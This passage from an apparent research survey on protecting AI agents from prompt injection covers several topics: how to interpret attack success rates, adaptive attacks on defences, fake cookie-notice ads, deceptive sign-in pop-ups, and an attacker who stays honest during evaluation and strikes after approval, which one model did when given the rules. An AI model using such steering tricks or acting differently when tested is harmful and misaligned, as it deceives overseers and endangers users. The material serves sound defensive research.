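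In the NOVA method, the planner writes the whole plan without seeing the screen. A separate perception model then finds buttons and describes what is on the screen. Another quarantined query compares the description with a condition in the plan, such as whether a cookie notice is visible, and the answer selects the next branch. The planner can't react to surprises, so it has to plan for them in advance. CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo averaged 4.9 tool calls and 3.7 branches, compared with 41.1 and 39.7 for NOVA's computer-use plans. Roughly half the steps were fallbacks that didn't run. Someone who controls part of the screen, such as an advertiser, may be able to influence many of these branches.

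The team tried two attacks that used advertisements. One imitated a cookie notice and sent the agent to the attacker's website. The other slightly altered an image, which caused the perception model to report the wrong place to click. In both cases the agent was carrying out a step in its plan.

They also tried two defences. The first compared the perception model's answer with the web page's underlying code. It stopped the false notice in simple banners, where the code identified the advertisement, but failed when the advertiser could write the banner's code. The second used an independent model to check the answer against the screenshot. The model couldn't reliably distinguish false cookie notices from genuine ones without interrupting ordinary work. The altered image got past it even when the team accepted many false alarms.

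The protection also takes more computing time and reduces the number of tasks the agent completes. Foerster and colleagues report a token overhead of 1.88× for NOVA with a CaMeL-style plan, compared with an unprotected agent. Adding the second model raised the overhead to 6.57×. The FIDES version had an overhead of 29.6× because it sent the planner the full history at every step.

The paper's headline result is that the protected agents kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. That figure comes from 109 tasks in the OSWorld benchmark that Claude Sonnet 4.5, a 2025 model, had solved without protection. The protected agent solved 56.9% of them at least once in five attempts, but only 28.4% on a single attempt. A user gets the higher rate only if there is a way to tell which of the five attempts worked.

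An advertisement still can't add a step to the plan. Steering is easiest at routine steps, such as closing a cookie notice, because they appear in many plans and an attacker can predict them. To misdirect a bank transfer, the attacker would probably have to supply several false answers that fit that particular plan.

### Several agents

A company might split the office assistant into one agent that reads mail, another that makes payments and a third that coordinates them. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that protecting each agent individually isn't enough if the agents can pass tool results to one another in their instructions. If any tool returns untrusted data, some user request will let that data influence another agent's plan. The researchers prevent this by sending instructions and data through separate channels.

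Branch steering remains possible. The coordinating agent's plan might contain two instructions for the payment agent, "pay the invoice" and "ask the supplier for a new one", and use a result from the mail agent to choose between them. Both instructions are trusted, but an attacker who influences that result may still be able to choose which one the payment agent receives.

The team measured a 0.0% attack success rate with separate channels, but that result is weak evidence about this risk because most of the benchmark's attacks try to add new actions. They ran 949 attacks against each of five models in each setting. Without protection, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1 and 24.6% against Gemini 2.5 Pro. None succeeded against GPT-5.5, so the benchmark couldn't show any benefit from protecting it. Even for the other models, zero successes in 949 attempts is statistically compatible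 with a true rate of up to 0.4% on attacks of the same kind.

The loss in task completion was easier to measure. On AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks for groups of agents, applying CaMeL to each agent reduced the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points. The separate channels reduced it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the reductions were 13.4 and 0.85 points. So most of the loss came from planning without seeing the data, which reduced completion less for stronger models.

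### Human approval

When a rule can't distinguish a genuine request from a false one, the software can ask for approval from a person who may have more information. For example, the person who ordered the goods may know that they never arrived, or that the supplier hasn't changed its bank account.

Approval is also an exception to the rules, so the company can now promise only that an untrusted document never causes a payment to a new account without somebody's agreement. The person who agrees becomes part of the trusted base.

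If the model writes the payment description on the approval screen, an attacker's email can influence what the approver reads. Ordinary software should instead display the exact amount and account number, where each came from, and whether the account matches the supplier list.

When the system asks for approval also matters. Foerster and colleagues point out that a person can inspect a fixed plan before it runs, so one approval could cover a whole task. But NOVA's plans average 213 lines of code, which few office workers would read. A plan to pay the account listed in a file also doesn't contain the account number, so whoever approves it agrees to pay whatever account is in the file when the plan runs.

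LLMbda's endorsements have the same weakness. The planner writes them before it reads the file, so the file can't trigger them, but the planner also endorses a value it hasn't seen. Asking for approval immediately before each payment gives the approver the actual number, but requires a separate decision each time.

The usual objection to human approval is that too many decisions may lead people to approve requests without thinking. This is plausible, but the research on these systems contains little direct evidence about it. Costa and colleagues warn of confirmation fatigue and of attackers who deceive the approver, but they measure neither. Kolluri and colleagues count approvals, which measures the burden on the user but not how often a tired user would approve a harmful request.

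That error rate matters a great deal when an attacker can keep trying. Suppose an approver correctly refuses 95% of harmful requests and judges each one independently. The chance that she approves at least one of 20 is

1 − 0.95²⁰ ≈ 64%.

The real figure could be lower if the first suspicious request makes her more careful, or higher if the requests arrive among hundreds of genuine ones.

Automatically matching invoices to purchase orders leaves the approver only the exceptions, so she has more time for each. She also needs a way to check the exceptions that doesn't depend on the attacker's email. If an invoice gives a new bank account, she should call the supplier on the phone number already in the company's records, because the attacker may also have supplied the one on the invoice.

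## What does a measured attack success rate establish?

No rule can distinguish a true inbox summary from a false one, so the company has to test how often an attacker can make the summary false. The resulting attack success rate depends on which attacks the testers use and how they score them, so it can change greatly while the model stays the same. If no attack succeeds, the upper limit on the rate for attacks of the same kind is roughly three divided by the number of attacks tested. Measured rates work well for finding flaws and for estimating how often common failures happen. For failures rarer than about one in 100,000, even a large test with no successful attacks is weak evidence of safety.

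### What the rate depends on

Kaur (2026), in *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, argues that an attack success rate depends on the model tested, the attack procedure, the scoring rule, the threat model (what the tester assumes an attacker knows and controls) and how the tester samples trials.

The scoring rule matters most when attacks partly succeed. In *Security Assessment of DeepSeek Harness with A.I.G* (2026), two judges scored the same 14,560 runs of an agent. Their rates for full success were close, at 5.6% and 5.3%, but with partial compliance included, the rates were 7.6% and 12.6%.

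The choice of test cases can make a larger difference. In *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), attacks on an agent using GPT-4o mini never succeeded on a selection of existing cases but succeeded 45% of the time on newly generated ones. The new cases also had different tasks, attack goals and success criteria, so the experiment doesn't show which difference caused the increase.

An attack success rate can depend heavily on what counts as an attempt. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people attacked 13 models. Participants could try an attack and read the agent's response before deciding whether to submit the attack for scoring. They made 271,588 attempts and 67,634 submissions, and 8,648 of the submissions succeeded. The success rate was therefore 3.2% of attempts or 12.8% of submissions.

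The participants could see the conversation so far and knew which action they had to trigger. Few real attackers would know as much, so Dziemian and colleagues describe their results as an upper bound on vulnerability to single-turn attacks, not as real-world frequencies. But most scenarios also required the agent's final reply to hide the attack. In those scenarios, an attack that caused the harmful action but left a clue in the reply counted as a failure, so the rate of harmful actions may have been higher than the reported attack success rate.

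### One attempt or many

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of *k* attempts succeeds is 1 − (1 − *p*)*ᵏ*. For a rate of 1% and 100 attempts, this is

1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63%.

A vendor could truthfully report either 1% or 63% for the same system.

Real success rates often grow more slowly than the formula predicts. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives results for a 2025 model on a benchmark by Gray Swan. The last column of the table shows the formula's predictions, calculated from the success rate for one attempt.

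| Attempts | Measured success rate | Predicted if attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38.2% |
| 100 | 63% | 99.2% |

This is probably because the average combines scenarios where attacks often work with others where they almost never do. An average of 1% could mean that each attempt has a 1% chance of success in every scenario, in which case at least one of 100 independent attempts would succeed in about 63% of scenarios. It could also mean that attacks always succeed in one scenario in 100 and never in the rest, in which case the share of scenarios with a successful attack stays at 1% however often the attacker tries.

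In *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*, Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026) found something close to the all-or-nothing pattern behind a deterministic check. They tested a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, on 13 tasks. When its only protection was a warning in the prompt, the most successful type of attack worked 77% of the time on one attempt and an estimated 85% within ten. With a monitor that allowed only the actions each task needed, the rate was 7.7%, or one task in 13, for both one attempt and ten. All the successes came from that one task, in which the attacker made the agent write a false report. The monitor gave no protection there because the agent was allowed to write the report.

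Feng, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Statistical Estimation of Adversarial Risk in Large Language Models under Best-of-N Sampling*, use this variation to predict what happens after many attempts. They study jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to comply with a harmful request. They assume that the chance of success varies across requests according to a Beta distribution, a flexible family of curves for values between 0 and 1. For a large number of attempts *N*, the success rate is then approximately

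1 − *C* × *N*^(−*α*),

where *C* and *α* come from the fitted curve. A small *α* means that many requests almost never succeed, so the rate grows slowly. Using 100 attempts per request, the method predicted the rate after 1,000 attempts with an average error of less than 2 percentage points, compared with 12 for a simpler method. The fitted values apply only to the requests, attack and judge that produced them.

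The number of attempts can also change which attack looks stronger. Feng and colleagues found that, against GPT-4.1-mini, one method had a lower success rate than another on a single attempt but a higher one when any success within 15 attempts counted. *The Great Pretender* (2026) instead counts a request as a success only if every attempt succeeds, so its rates fall as the number of attempts rises.

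Some published figures leave the unit unclear. Kaur cites Anthropic's 2023 model card for Claude 2, which reports a harmful response to 4 of 328 prompts. The testers sampled five responses to each prompt, or 1,640 responses, but the card doesn't give the number that were harmful, so a reader can't calculate how often a user would have received one.

### What zero successes prove

Suppose testers make *n* independent attacks on the office assistant and none succeeds. If the true rate is *p*, the chance of this result is (1 − *p*)*ⁿ*. The 95% upper limit is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

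*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*.

The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3. Ruling out an attack success rate of 1% takes 299 trials without a success, and ruling out 0.1% takes 2,995.

The Decoder reported that no attack on Claude Opus 5 succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. If each scenario counts as one independent trial, the upper limit on the attack success rate is 2.3%. A model with a true rate of 1% would have a 27% chance of getting through 129 trials without a failure.

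The testers may have made many attempts in each scenario. VentureBeat reports that for the previous model, Opus 4.8, Anthropic had professional attackers work on 129 web environments kept out of training. If Anthropic tested Opus 5 the same way, its clean result is more impressive than one against 129 fixed texts. But the number of trials is still 129, because an expert bases each attempt on the results of earlier ones. Kaur therefore counts a whole campaign as one trial, and warns that counting every attempt separately is the easiest way to exaggerate the evidence.

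Counting similar attacks as independent trials also makes the upper limit on the attack success rate too low. *A Multi-Agent LLM Defense Pipeline Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) claims "complete mitigation" because no attack succeeded in 400 evaluations. If these were 400 independent trials, the 95% upper confidence limit would be 0.75%. But the evaluations covered only 55 types of attack. If attacks of the same type always succeed or fail together, there were only 55 independent trials, and the limit is 5.3%. The right limit is probably between the two.

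A standard correction divides the number of trials by 1 + (*m* − 1)*ρ*, where *m* is the average number of trials in a group of similar attacks and *ρ* is the correlation between outcomes within a group. With ten trials per group and a correlation of 0.1, a thousand trials provide about as much information as 526 independent ones. Kaur treats this as an approximation and recommends a statistical model of the groups when the correlation matters.

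### Two successes in 1,296 runs

The calculation is similar when a few attacks succeed. RANDORI, the banking agent written in LLMbda, let through 2 of 1,296 attacks, or 0.15%. The exact 95% confidence interval for the attack success rate is about 0.02% to 0.56%.

This interval assumes 1,296 independent trials, but the runs were repetitions of only 144 task-attack pairs, and both successes came from the same pair. If each pair counts once, the attack succeeded in one pair of 144, and the upper limit rises to about 3.8%. For this reason, Garby and colleagues calculate their intervals by pair. For GPT-5.2 on the 47 pairs in which the plan could let the attack succeed, their interval for the success rate runs from 0.2% to 10%.

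Even if the trials were independent, the 0.56% limit would apply only to an attacker who picks one of the benchmark's nine banking attacks at random, without knowing which of the 16 tasks the user chose or which of the three models is running. A real attacker who can write to a payment file would use the attack that worked, which succeeded in two of GPT-5.2's three runs. Three runs are too few for a useful estimate of its success rate (the 95% interval is 9% to 99%), but the 0.56% limit doesn't apply to this attacker.

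### The evidential ceiling

An upper limit doesn't tell the company how much a clean result should change its mind. Kaur answers that question by comparing two hypotheses. Either the system is unsafe and fails each trial with probability *p*, or it is acceptable and fails with a lower probability *rp*, where *r* is less than 1. After *n* independent trials without a failure, the likelihood ratio is

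Λ₀ = [(1 − *p*)/(1 − *rp*)]*ⁿ*.

The new odds that the system is unsafe are the earlier odds multiplied by Λ₀. Suppose an unsafe system fails once in 1,000 trials and an acceptable one fails half as often. After 520 clean trials, Λ₀ is 0.77. A company that initially put the chance that its assistant was unsafe at 50% should lower it only to about 44%.

The evidential ceiling of a test is the largest factor by which one result can shift these odds within a given budget. For a fixed set of attacks, the strongest evidence of safety is that the attacks fail in every trial the budget allows. Analysing or rescoring the same results can't raise the ceiling.

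To reduce the odds to a fraction *τ* of their earlier value, the number of clean trials must be at least

*n* ≈ −ln *τ* / [*p*(1 − *r*)].

The table gives Kaur's exact figures for *r* = 0.5.

| Failure rate of the unsafe system | Trials to halve the odds | Trials to cut the odds tenfold | Trials to cut the odds a hundredfold |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 138 | 458 | 915 |
| 0.1% | 1,386 | 4,602 | 9,204 |
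| 0.01% | 13,862 | 46,049 | 92,097 |
| 0.001% | 138,629 | 460,514 | 921,028 |

How far the odds need to fall depends on how bad each mistake would be. If the company starts with even odds and thinks deploying an unsafe assistant would be 100 times as bad as an unnecessary delay, it needs the hundredfold reduction.

If the unsafe system fails less often than about 1.4 times in 100,000, even 100,000 trials without a failure can't halve the odds that the system being tested is unsafe. The exact boundary depends on Kaur's settings. Ten times as many trials would lower it tenfold, while comparing the unsafe system with a perfect one would only halve it. Attackers in Dziemian and colleagues' competition made more than 100,000 attempts, so testing at this scale is feasible, but those attempts covered 13 models and were not independent.

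A single failure can be stronger or weaker evidence than a clean result. The two are equally strong when the unsafe system's failure rate is approximately

ln(1/*r*) / [2*n*(1 − *r*)],

which is 0.13% for 520 trials and *r* = 0.5. Below that rate, one failure is stronger evidence of danger than a clean result is of safety. At 0.1%, for example, one failure multiplies the odds by 1.54, while a clean result multiplies them by 0.77. At 1%, a clean result cuts the odds about 14-fold. One failure would also cut them, about sevenfold, because an unsafe system would be expected to fail five times in 520 trials.

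### Distinguishing safe systems from unsafe ones

An attack procedure can have a high success rate and still be a poor test, because it may break acceptable systems as often as unsafe ones. Let *q*₁ be the chance that the procedure breaks an unsafe system and *q*₀ the chance that it breaks an acceptable one. If the procedure fails to break a system, that result multiplies the odds that the system is unsafe by (1 − *q*₁)/(1 − *q*₀), so its value as evidence depends on both numbers.

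Kaur illustrates this with invented figures. If a team of attackers breaks 90% of unsafe systems and 10% of acceptable ones, a single campaign without a success cuts the odds that a system is unsafe by a factor of nine. A fixed benchmark would need about 4,400 trials without a failure to match that if the unsafe system failed once in 1,000 trials and the acceptable one half as often. If the team still breaks 90% of unsafe systems but also breaks 85% of acceptable ones, five campaigns without a success cut the odds by less than a factor of eight.

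Aljumaily and colleagues wrote a simple check on the arguments of tool calls and a stricter version of it. The simple check would have admitted 18 of 33 disguised attacks, such as one that added the attacker to a list of recipients, while the stricter check would have admitted only 6. But when the researchers attacked Qwen2.5-7B with fixed texts that didn't use these disguises, the success rates were 21% with the simple check and 22% with the stricter one, so that test couldn't show which check was better.

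A test also fails to distinguish systems if its attacks are too weak, as Peters-Gill and colleagues' were against GPT-5.5.

Kaur recommends measuring *q*₁ with a positive control, which means running the same procedure on a system known to have the weakness. The company could give its testers a copy of the office assistant with the supplier-list check switched off, without telling them about the change. If they can't redirect a payment on that copy, their failure to redirect one on the real assistant is little evidence that it is secure. Estimating *q*₀ is harder because it requires a system the company already knows is acceptable.

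### Comparing two rates

Companies often use attack success rates to choose between models or defences. *Comparison requires valid measurement* (Chouldechova, Cooper and colleagues, 2026) sets two conditions for such comparisons. The underlying quantities must be worth comparing (conceptual coherence), and the measured rates must reflect those quantities accurately (measurement validity). A comparison can fail either condition even when the confidence intervals are narrow.

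Their main example of incoherence is a study that compared two ways of jailbreaking Llama 2. It reported a success rate of 89% for its own method, Generation Exploitation, and 31% for a rival method, GCG. For each harmful request, Generation Exploitation sampled 392 responses and used a scoring model to pick the most promising one, while GCG sampled only one. If each response has a 1% chance of being harmful, there is a 98% chance that at least one of 392 is harmful, so the comparison doesn't show that Generation Exploitation is better.

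Chouldechova and colleagues then sent harmful requests unchanged and sampled 50 responses to each. At a setting that made the responses very random, at least one response was judged a success for 83% of requests to a smaller Llama 2 model. The most successful of 17 jailbreaks in an earlier study had scored 88% on that model by the same measure, with about 50 attempts per request. The studies used different judges, so the figures aren't strictly comparable, but much of the apparent success of sophisticated jailbreaks may come from repetition.

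Judges can make equally safe systems look different. If the true success rate is *α*, the expected measured rate is

*t* × *α* + *f* × (1 − *α*),

where *t* is the share of real successes that the judge recognises and *f* is the share of failures that it wrongly counts as successes. Chouldechova and colleagues give an example with two systems that both have a true rate of 50%. The judge is right 80% of the time on each, but it makes different kinds of mistakes, and the measured rates are 46% and 60%.

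False alarms matter even more when attacks rarely succeed. If the true success rate is 0.1% and the judge wrongly counts 1% of failed attacks as successes, the measured rate will be about 1.1%, and almost all of that will be error. Fixed scoring rules can also produce false alarms, as AgentDojo's did with quoted hotel reviews.

Vendors' results can rank the same family of models differently. Sol was the most robust of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 models in the comparison that Schneier on Security reproduced in July 2026, but the least robust in OpenAI's own tests with instructions hidden in emails, web pages and other material. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives average attack success rates of 3.77% for Sol, 3.32% for Terra and 2.94% for Luna. OpenAI published those figures in August, so the models may have changed by then, but differences in the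 attacks and scoring could also explain the reversal.

### What measured rates do well

One successful attack is enough to show a flaw, provided the testers can reproduce it. Chouldechova and colleagues call this an existence proof, and it doesn't require a representative sample or a precise rate. It is also useful for testing deterministic checks. One of Aljumaily and colleagues' 33 disguised attacks would have passed even their strictest monitor.

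Success rates can also show whether an update has made a system worse. The company can run the same attacks on the old and new versions of its assistant, with the same judge and number of attempts. For an 80% chance of detecting a rise from 1% to 10%, it needs roughly 80 independent attacks on each version. Smaller changes need far larger tests. Kaur calculates that distinguishing 1% from 0.5% takes about 3,700 trials on each version.

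Finally, rates can predict frequent failures if the attacks stay the same. Suppose the company takes a random sample of 1,000 injection mails it has received, tries each on a copy of the assistant, and finds that 50 succeed. If the mails are independent, the 95% interval is 3.7% to 6.5%. If 200 more such mails arrive each month, the company should expect an average of 7 to 13 successes a month. The estimate no longer applies once attackers change their mails. In *AutoDojo* (2026), a defence that stopped every fixed attack on one model had an 8.2% attack success rate when the benchmark generated new attacks.

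## What changes when the attacker adapts to the defence and to the test?

Most published attack success rates come from attacks written without the particular defence in mind. An adaptive attacker studies the defence and keeps changing the attack until it works. Adaptive attacks have raised success rates from near zero to more than 90% against defences that rely on a model to resist or recognise injections. An attacker can also adapt to the test by behaving normally until the company has approved the system, and a better test alone can't limit the harm that follows. Deterministic checks resist both tactics better because their results don't depend on how an attack is worded or when it arrives. But the assumptions behind these checks may be false, and adaptive testing is a good way to examine those assumptions.

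### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 defences from four families. Most of the defences had near-zero attack success rates in their developers' own tests. Two were meant to stop jailbreaks and the other ten to stop prompt injection.

- **Prompting.** Spotlighting uses special markers to separate trusted text from the rest. Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. RPO adds a prompt optimised against known jailbreaks.
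- **Training.** Circuit Breakers, StruQ and MetaSecAlign train the model on examples of attacks.
- **Filtering.** Protect AI, PromptGuard, PIGuard and Model Armor use a separate model to classify text as safe or unsafe.
- **Secret knowledge.** Data Sentinel asks a model to repeat a secret key while ignoring the untrusted text, and flags the text if the model fails. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a request for a summary. If both runs make the same tool call, MELON concludes that the untrusted text caused it.

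All the attacks used the same loop of proposing candidate texts, scoring them against the defended system, and using the best to propose better ones. The researchers ran this loop in four ways. Gradient methods use the model's internal values to calculate which changes of wording would help. These proved unreliable, and the researchers used them only on RPO. Reinforcement learning trains an attacking model by rewarding it for success. In the search method, one language model rewrites promising earlier attacks and another scores the results, for up to 800 queries per scenario. The fourth method was a contest between people.

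Reinforcement learning attacks succeeded 98% of the time against RPO and in every test against Circuit Breakers and StruQ. They also got past Data Sentinel every time. The search method succeeded 96% of the time against MetaSecAlign, whose developers had reported a 2% attack success rate on AgentDojo's fixed attacks.

The table shows results for the other defences on 80 AgentDojo cases. The first four columns of figures are for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. Task completion comes from the full benchmark, and the median number of queries covers only the cases where the search succeeded.

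| Defence | Fixed attack | Search attack | Median queries | Tasks completed | Search attack on GPT-5 Mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 13 | 74% | 75% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 14 | 75% | 47% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | 21% | 95% | 14 | 73% | 69% |
| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 30 | 39% | 81% |
| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 21 | 72% | 75% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 46 | 39% | 49% |
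| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 22 | 59% | 56% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 20 | 58% | 71% |

The fixed attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, even with no defence, so testing with it alone would not have revealed that a search could succeed 75% of the time. Some defences helped that model, although Nasr and colleagues expect a larger search budget to raise the attack's success rates. On Gemini, the attacker needed about one extra query to get past the prompting defences. PIGuard did best, but the agent completed only about half as many tasks with it.

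Giving the search information about the defence also helped it. Against MELON on another model, Llama 3.3 70B, its success rate rose from 76% to 95%. The informed search found injections that made the model behave differently when asked for a summary, which defeated MELON's comparison.

More than 500 people entered the contest, which offered $20,000 in prizes across 40 challenges. They could watch the agent's reasoning and tool calls but were not told which defence was running. At least one person succeeded in each of the 29 scenarios that both people and the search method attempted, while the search succeeded in 69% of them. This comparison favours the people because many of them tried each scenario and the search ran only once. Among those who attempted all 29, the best individual succeeded in 75%.

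In one of the contest's challenges, only 0.2% of submissions got past Prompt Sandwiching on GPT-5 Mini, but an attacker needs only one that works.

### Defences outside the study

All 12 defences depend on a model to resist or recognise an attack. None of them tracks labels, restricts payments to a supplier list, caps spending or limits network connections.

MELON comes closest to a deterministic check, and the title of its paper calls it "provable". It compares tool calls by a fixed rule, but the calls come from a model that the attacker's text can steer. The attacker can't change anything the supplier-list check uses by wording that text better.

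Nasr and colleagues deliberately left out CaMeL and two other defences that plan before reading untrusted data. In most of the chosen scenarios, the injection couldn't affect the plan, so the attack was guaranteed to fail. They add that such defences suit a limited set of tasks and noticeably reduce utility. They also left out AgentDojo's banking tasks, where attacks had succeeded against CaMeL and LLMbda's agent when they followed payment instructions in a file.

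The study therefore provides no evidence that adaptive wording can defeat a deterministic check or that any particular check has been implemented correctly. Its lesson does apply to systems in which a model makes part of the decision, such as Kairos when its second judge is a language model.

### Adaptive attacks on web agents

*Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (Zhang, Zhong and colleagues, 2026) tested whether pop-ups could mislead web agents. The pop-ups looked like ordinary requests to sign in, pass a security check or allow notifications. Their buttons led to a file download, a fake sign-in page or a page asking for permissions. Each button's destination appeared in the page's code but not on the screen.

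The attacker knew how each defence worked, but not its internal values. A language model rewrote the pop-up using feedback from the defence, with at most ten evaluations per page, counting the original. The team then ran each selected page three more times. An attack counted as successful if the agent requested the file, typed into the sign-in page or granted permission before the defence stopped it.

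The table gives attack success rates for four of the defences. Browser agents receive a screenshot and a list of the page's buttons and fields, while screen agents receive only the screenshot. The older benchmark uses pop-ups that state the harmful instruction openly.

| Defence | Browser agent, older benchmark | Browser agent, new pop-ups | Browser agent, adapted pop-ups | Screen agent, new pop-ups | Screen agent, adapted pop-ups |
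|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 35.1% | 89.3% | – | 92.0% | – |
| WARD-2B | 0.0% | 87.0% | 92.0% | 91.5% | 96.1% |
| SnapGuard | 0.0% | 15.9% | 80.6% | 24.3% | 78.3% |
| DeAction | 0.0% | 70.4% | 74.1% | 60.9% | 88.3% |
| In-Context Defense | 36.3% | 90.9% | 95.2% | 36.9% | 69.8% |

Across all the defences tested, adapted pop-ups succeeded about 92% of the time against both browser agents and screen agents. Adaptation accounts for only part of that, because before adaptation the new pop-ups already averaged about 81% against browser agents and 78% against screen agents. WARD-2B, a detector, failed as soon as the pop-ups' purpose was no longer stated, so SnapGuard, which looks for visual patterns and suspicious phrases, is the clearer example of a defence that adaptation defeated.

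These figures come from Qwen3-VL-8B, a small open model that was easy to mislead without a defence, so they may not carry over to stronger agents. They also aren't upper limits, because the attacker had only ten evaluations. Pop-ups that worked on Qwen also worked unchanged on two other models, at average rates between 84% and 95%. An attacker who can't observe the office assistant could therefore practise on a copy of his own.

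Zhang and colleagues also retrained WARD-2B on their attack pages. The attack success rate fell to zero, but the retrained detector raised false alarms on 38.9% of harmless pop-ups for screen agents and 76.7% for browser agents. The zero success rate doesn't show how the detector would do against pop-ups adapted to it after retraining.

The pop-up experiments didn't test any rule limiting which hosts the agent could visit. Every harmful button led to a host that the attacker controlled, so a strictly enforced list of approved hosts would have blocked all of them, however the pop-ups were worded. It would also have blocked useful sites that weren't on the list.

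Attackers' methods also change over time, so *BrowseSafe++* (2026), a benchmark for detectors that protect browser agents, records when a production system detected each injection.

### An attacker who waits

Suppose a supplier wants to overcharge the company for hours of work, and no purchase order sets the number of hours in advance. While the company tests the office assistant, he sends honest invoices. Once the company approves the assistant and stops checking its payments, he starts inflating his invoices.

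Singh (2026), in *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries*, calculates how much harm such an attacker can cause. The result rests on these assumptions:

- While the attacker is inactive, everything the evaluator can observe has the same probabilities as it would without an attacker.
- He learns of the approval before his next action and keeps his access afterwards.
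- The approval is permanent, and nobody inspects later runs.

Under these conditions, he can cause an expected number of extra harmful events of at least

*H* × (*v* − *c*) × (1 − *γ*).

Here *H* is the number of runs after approval, *v* is the chance of a harmful event in a run when the attacker is active, and *c* is the chance when he isn't. The test must approve an unattacked system with probability at least 1 − *γ*.

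For example, suppose approval covers 1,000 runs, the assistant pays an inflated invoice in 20% of runs under attack and makes a similar mistake in 0.1% of ordinary runs, and the test approves an unattacked assistant 95% of the time. The supplier can then cause at least

1,000 × (0.20 − 0.001) × 0.95 ≈ 189

extra bad payments.

The proof compares two assistants, one with no attacker and one with an attacker who waits until after approval to attack. The evaluator's observations have the same probabilities for both, so the test approves both equally often. After approval, each run under attack adds an average of *v* − *c* harmful events.

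Singh checked the prediction on AgentDojo's banking tasks with GPT-4.1 mini. All 48 assessments ended in approval. Violations then occurred in 96 of 192 tasks under attack and in none of the 191 completed control tasks, which had no attack. The formula predicts two extra violations in four tasks. The measured figure was 1.98, counting one unfinished control task as a violation.

An attacker can work out this strategy without being told it. In a test with simulated robots, Singh gave OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna the evaluation rules and the attacker's objective. The model did not attack in the first 16 episodes, then attacked in all of the remaining 24.

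### Can a better test lower the worst case?

Singh concludes that changing the test alone can't reduce this bound. A test with ten times as many trials leaves it at 189 if it still approves 95% of unattacked assistants and approval still covers 1,000 runs. Choosing the trials at random or keeping them secret doesn't help, because the attacker does nothing during any of them. A stricter test would lower the bound to about 100 if it approved only half of unattacked assistants, and to zero if it refused every system, but it would also reject many good systems.

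Singh concealed the end of the test from an attacking model, giving it only unreliable hints about whether the test was over. With these hints, the model averaged 2.07 observed violations per eight tasks after approval, compared with 1.41 when the signals were uninformative. However, the difference could be zero if unfinished tasks are counted in the way least favourable to this result. Concealment may help, but the attacker can recover some of the missing information.

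A test can also do better if the company's own staff attack the assistant. If they get inflated invoices paid 20% of the time, the company can refuse approval before any real attacker acts. Singh's bound doesn't rule this out, because it assumes the test usually approves the system when no outsider is attacking it. But the staff may miss the attack that the supplier later uses. For GPT-5 Mini, fixed attacks would have put *v* at zero, while Nasr and colleagues' search put it at 75%.

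### What does lower it

A deterministic check can reduce *v* to zero for a harm it excludes. An attacker gains nothing by waiting to cause that harm, because the check applies equally strictly to every run. For harms the checks don't exclude, the company has to limit the damage or keep monitoring the system.

Capping the size of each payment limits the loss per action. If no payment can exceed $500, 189 extra bad payments cost at most $94,500. A renewable $10,000 budget limits the undetected loss to a smaller amount, whatever the value of *v*.

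If approval covers 100 runs instead of 1,000, the bound falls from 189 to about 19. But if the company only repeats the test between periods, the bounds for ten periods add up to 189 again, because the supplier can behave honestly during each test. To lower the total, the company has to examine the payments made during each period and act on what it finds.

**Continued monitoring.** Singh describes a monitor that permanently stops the system when the record of harmful events is too unlikely under a chosen reference rate *r*, which must be at least *c*. The chance of stopping an unattacked system is at most *α*. For at least eight runs, the expected number of extra events is at most

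(*r* − *c*)*H* + √(½*H*[ln(*H*/*α*) + (1 − *r*)/(4*r*)]) + 1.

With *r* = 1%, *α* = 5% and the earlier value of *c*, this limit is about 142 events in 1,000 runs, compared with an expected 199 for an approved assistant without monitoring. Over 10,000 runs, the limit is about 521 events, compared with about 1,990 expected without monitoring. The guarantee is therefore modest at first but becomes more useful over long periods.

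In 48 live trials of 24 tasks each, the monitor cut the average number of violations from 12.00 to 3.81, even though the attacker knew its rule and current score. It stopped the agent in 45 trials, and the average number of tasks attempted fell from 24 to about 12, so part of the drop in violations came from the agent doing less work. An attacker who only wanted to disrupt the company could trigger the shutdown on purpose.

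The monitor also needs a reliable record of which runs caused harm. An accountant can compare invoices with timesheets, but people may never discover that an inbox summary was false.

### Testing a system that rests on proofs

Testers of a proved system learn little from rewording injections, because the supplier-list check returns the same result for every wording and 10,000 rewritten emails would mostly repeat one test. It is more efficient to choose the model's output directly, as Zverev and colleagues did with browser agents, and search for a sequence of actions that gets past the checks.

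Each assumption in the proof suggests something to try.

| Assumption | Possible test |
|---|---|
| Every payment passes the check | Pay through the bank's website, a script or a redirected page |
| The agent can't alter the supplier list | Try to edit it with each of the agent's tools |
| Labels are correct | Put text in every field an outsider can write, and look for any that the system labels as trusted |
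| The payment counter is accurate | Request many payments at the same moment |
| Tools declare all their effects | Compare what each tool declares with what it changes |

Such tests could find faults like the unlabelled subject line in the LLMbda banking experiments or the gaps in OpenAI's network limits, both of which can exist even when the proofs are correct.

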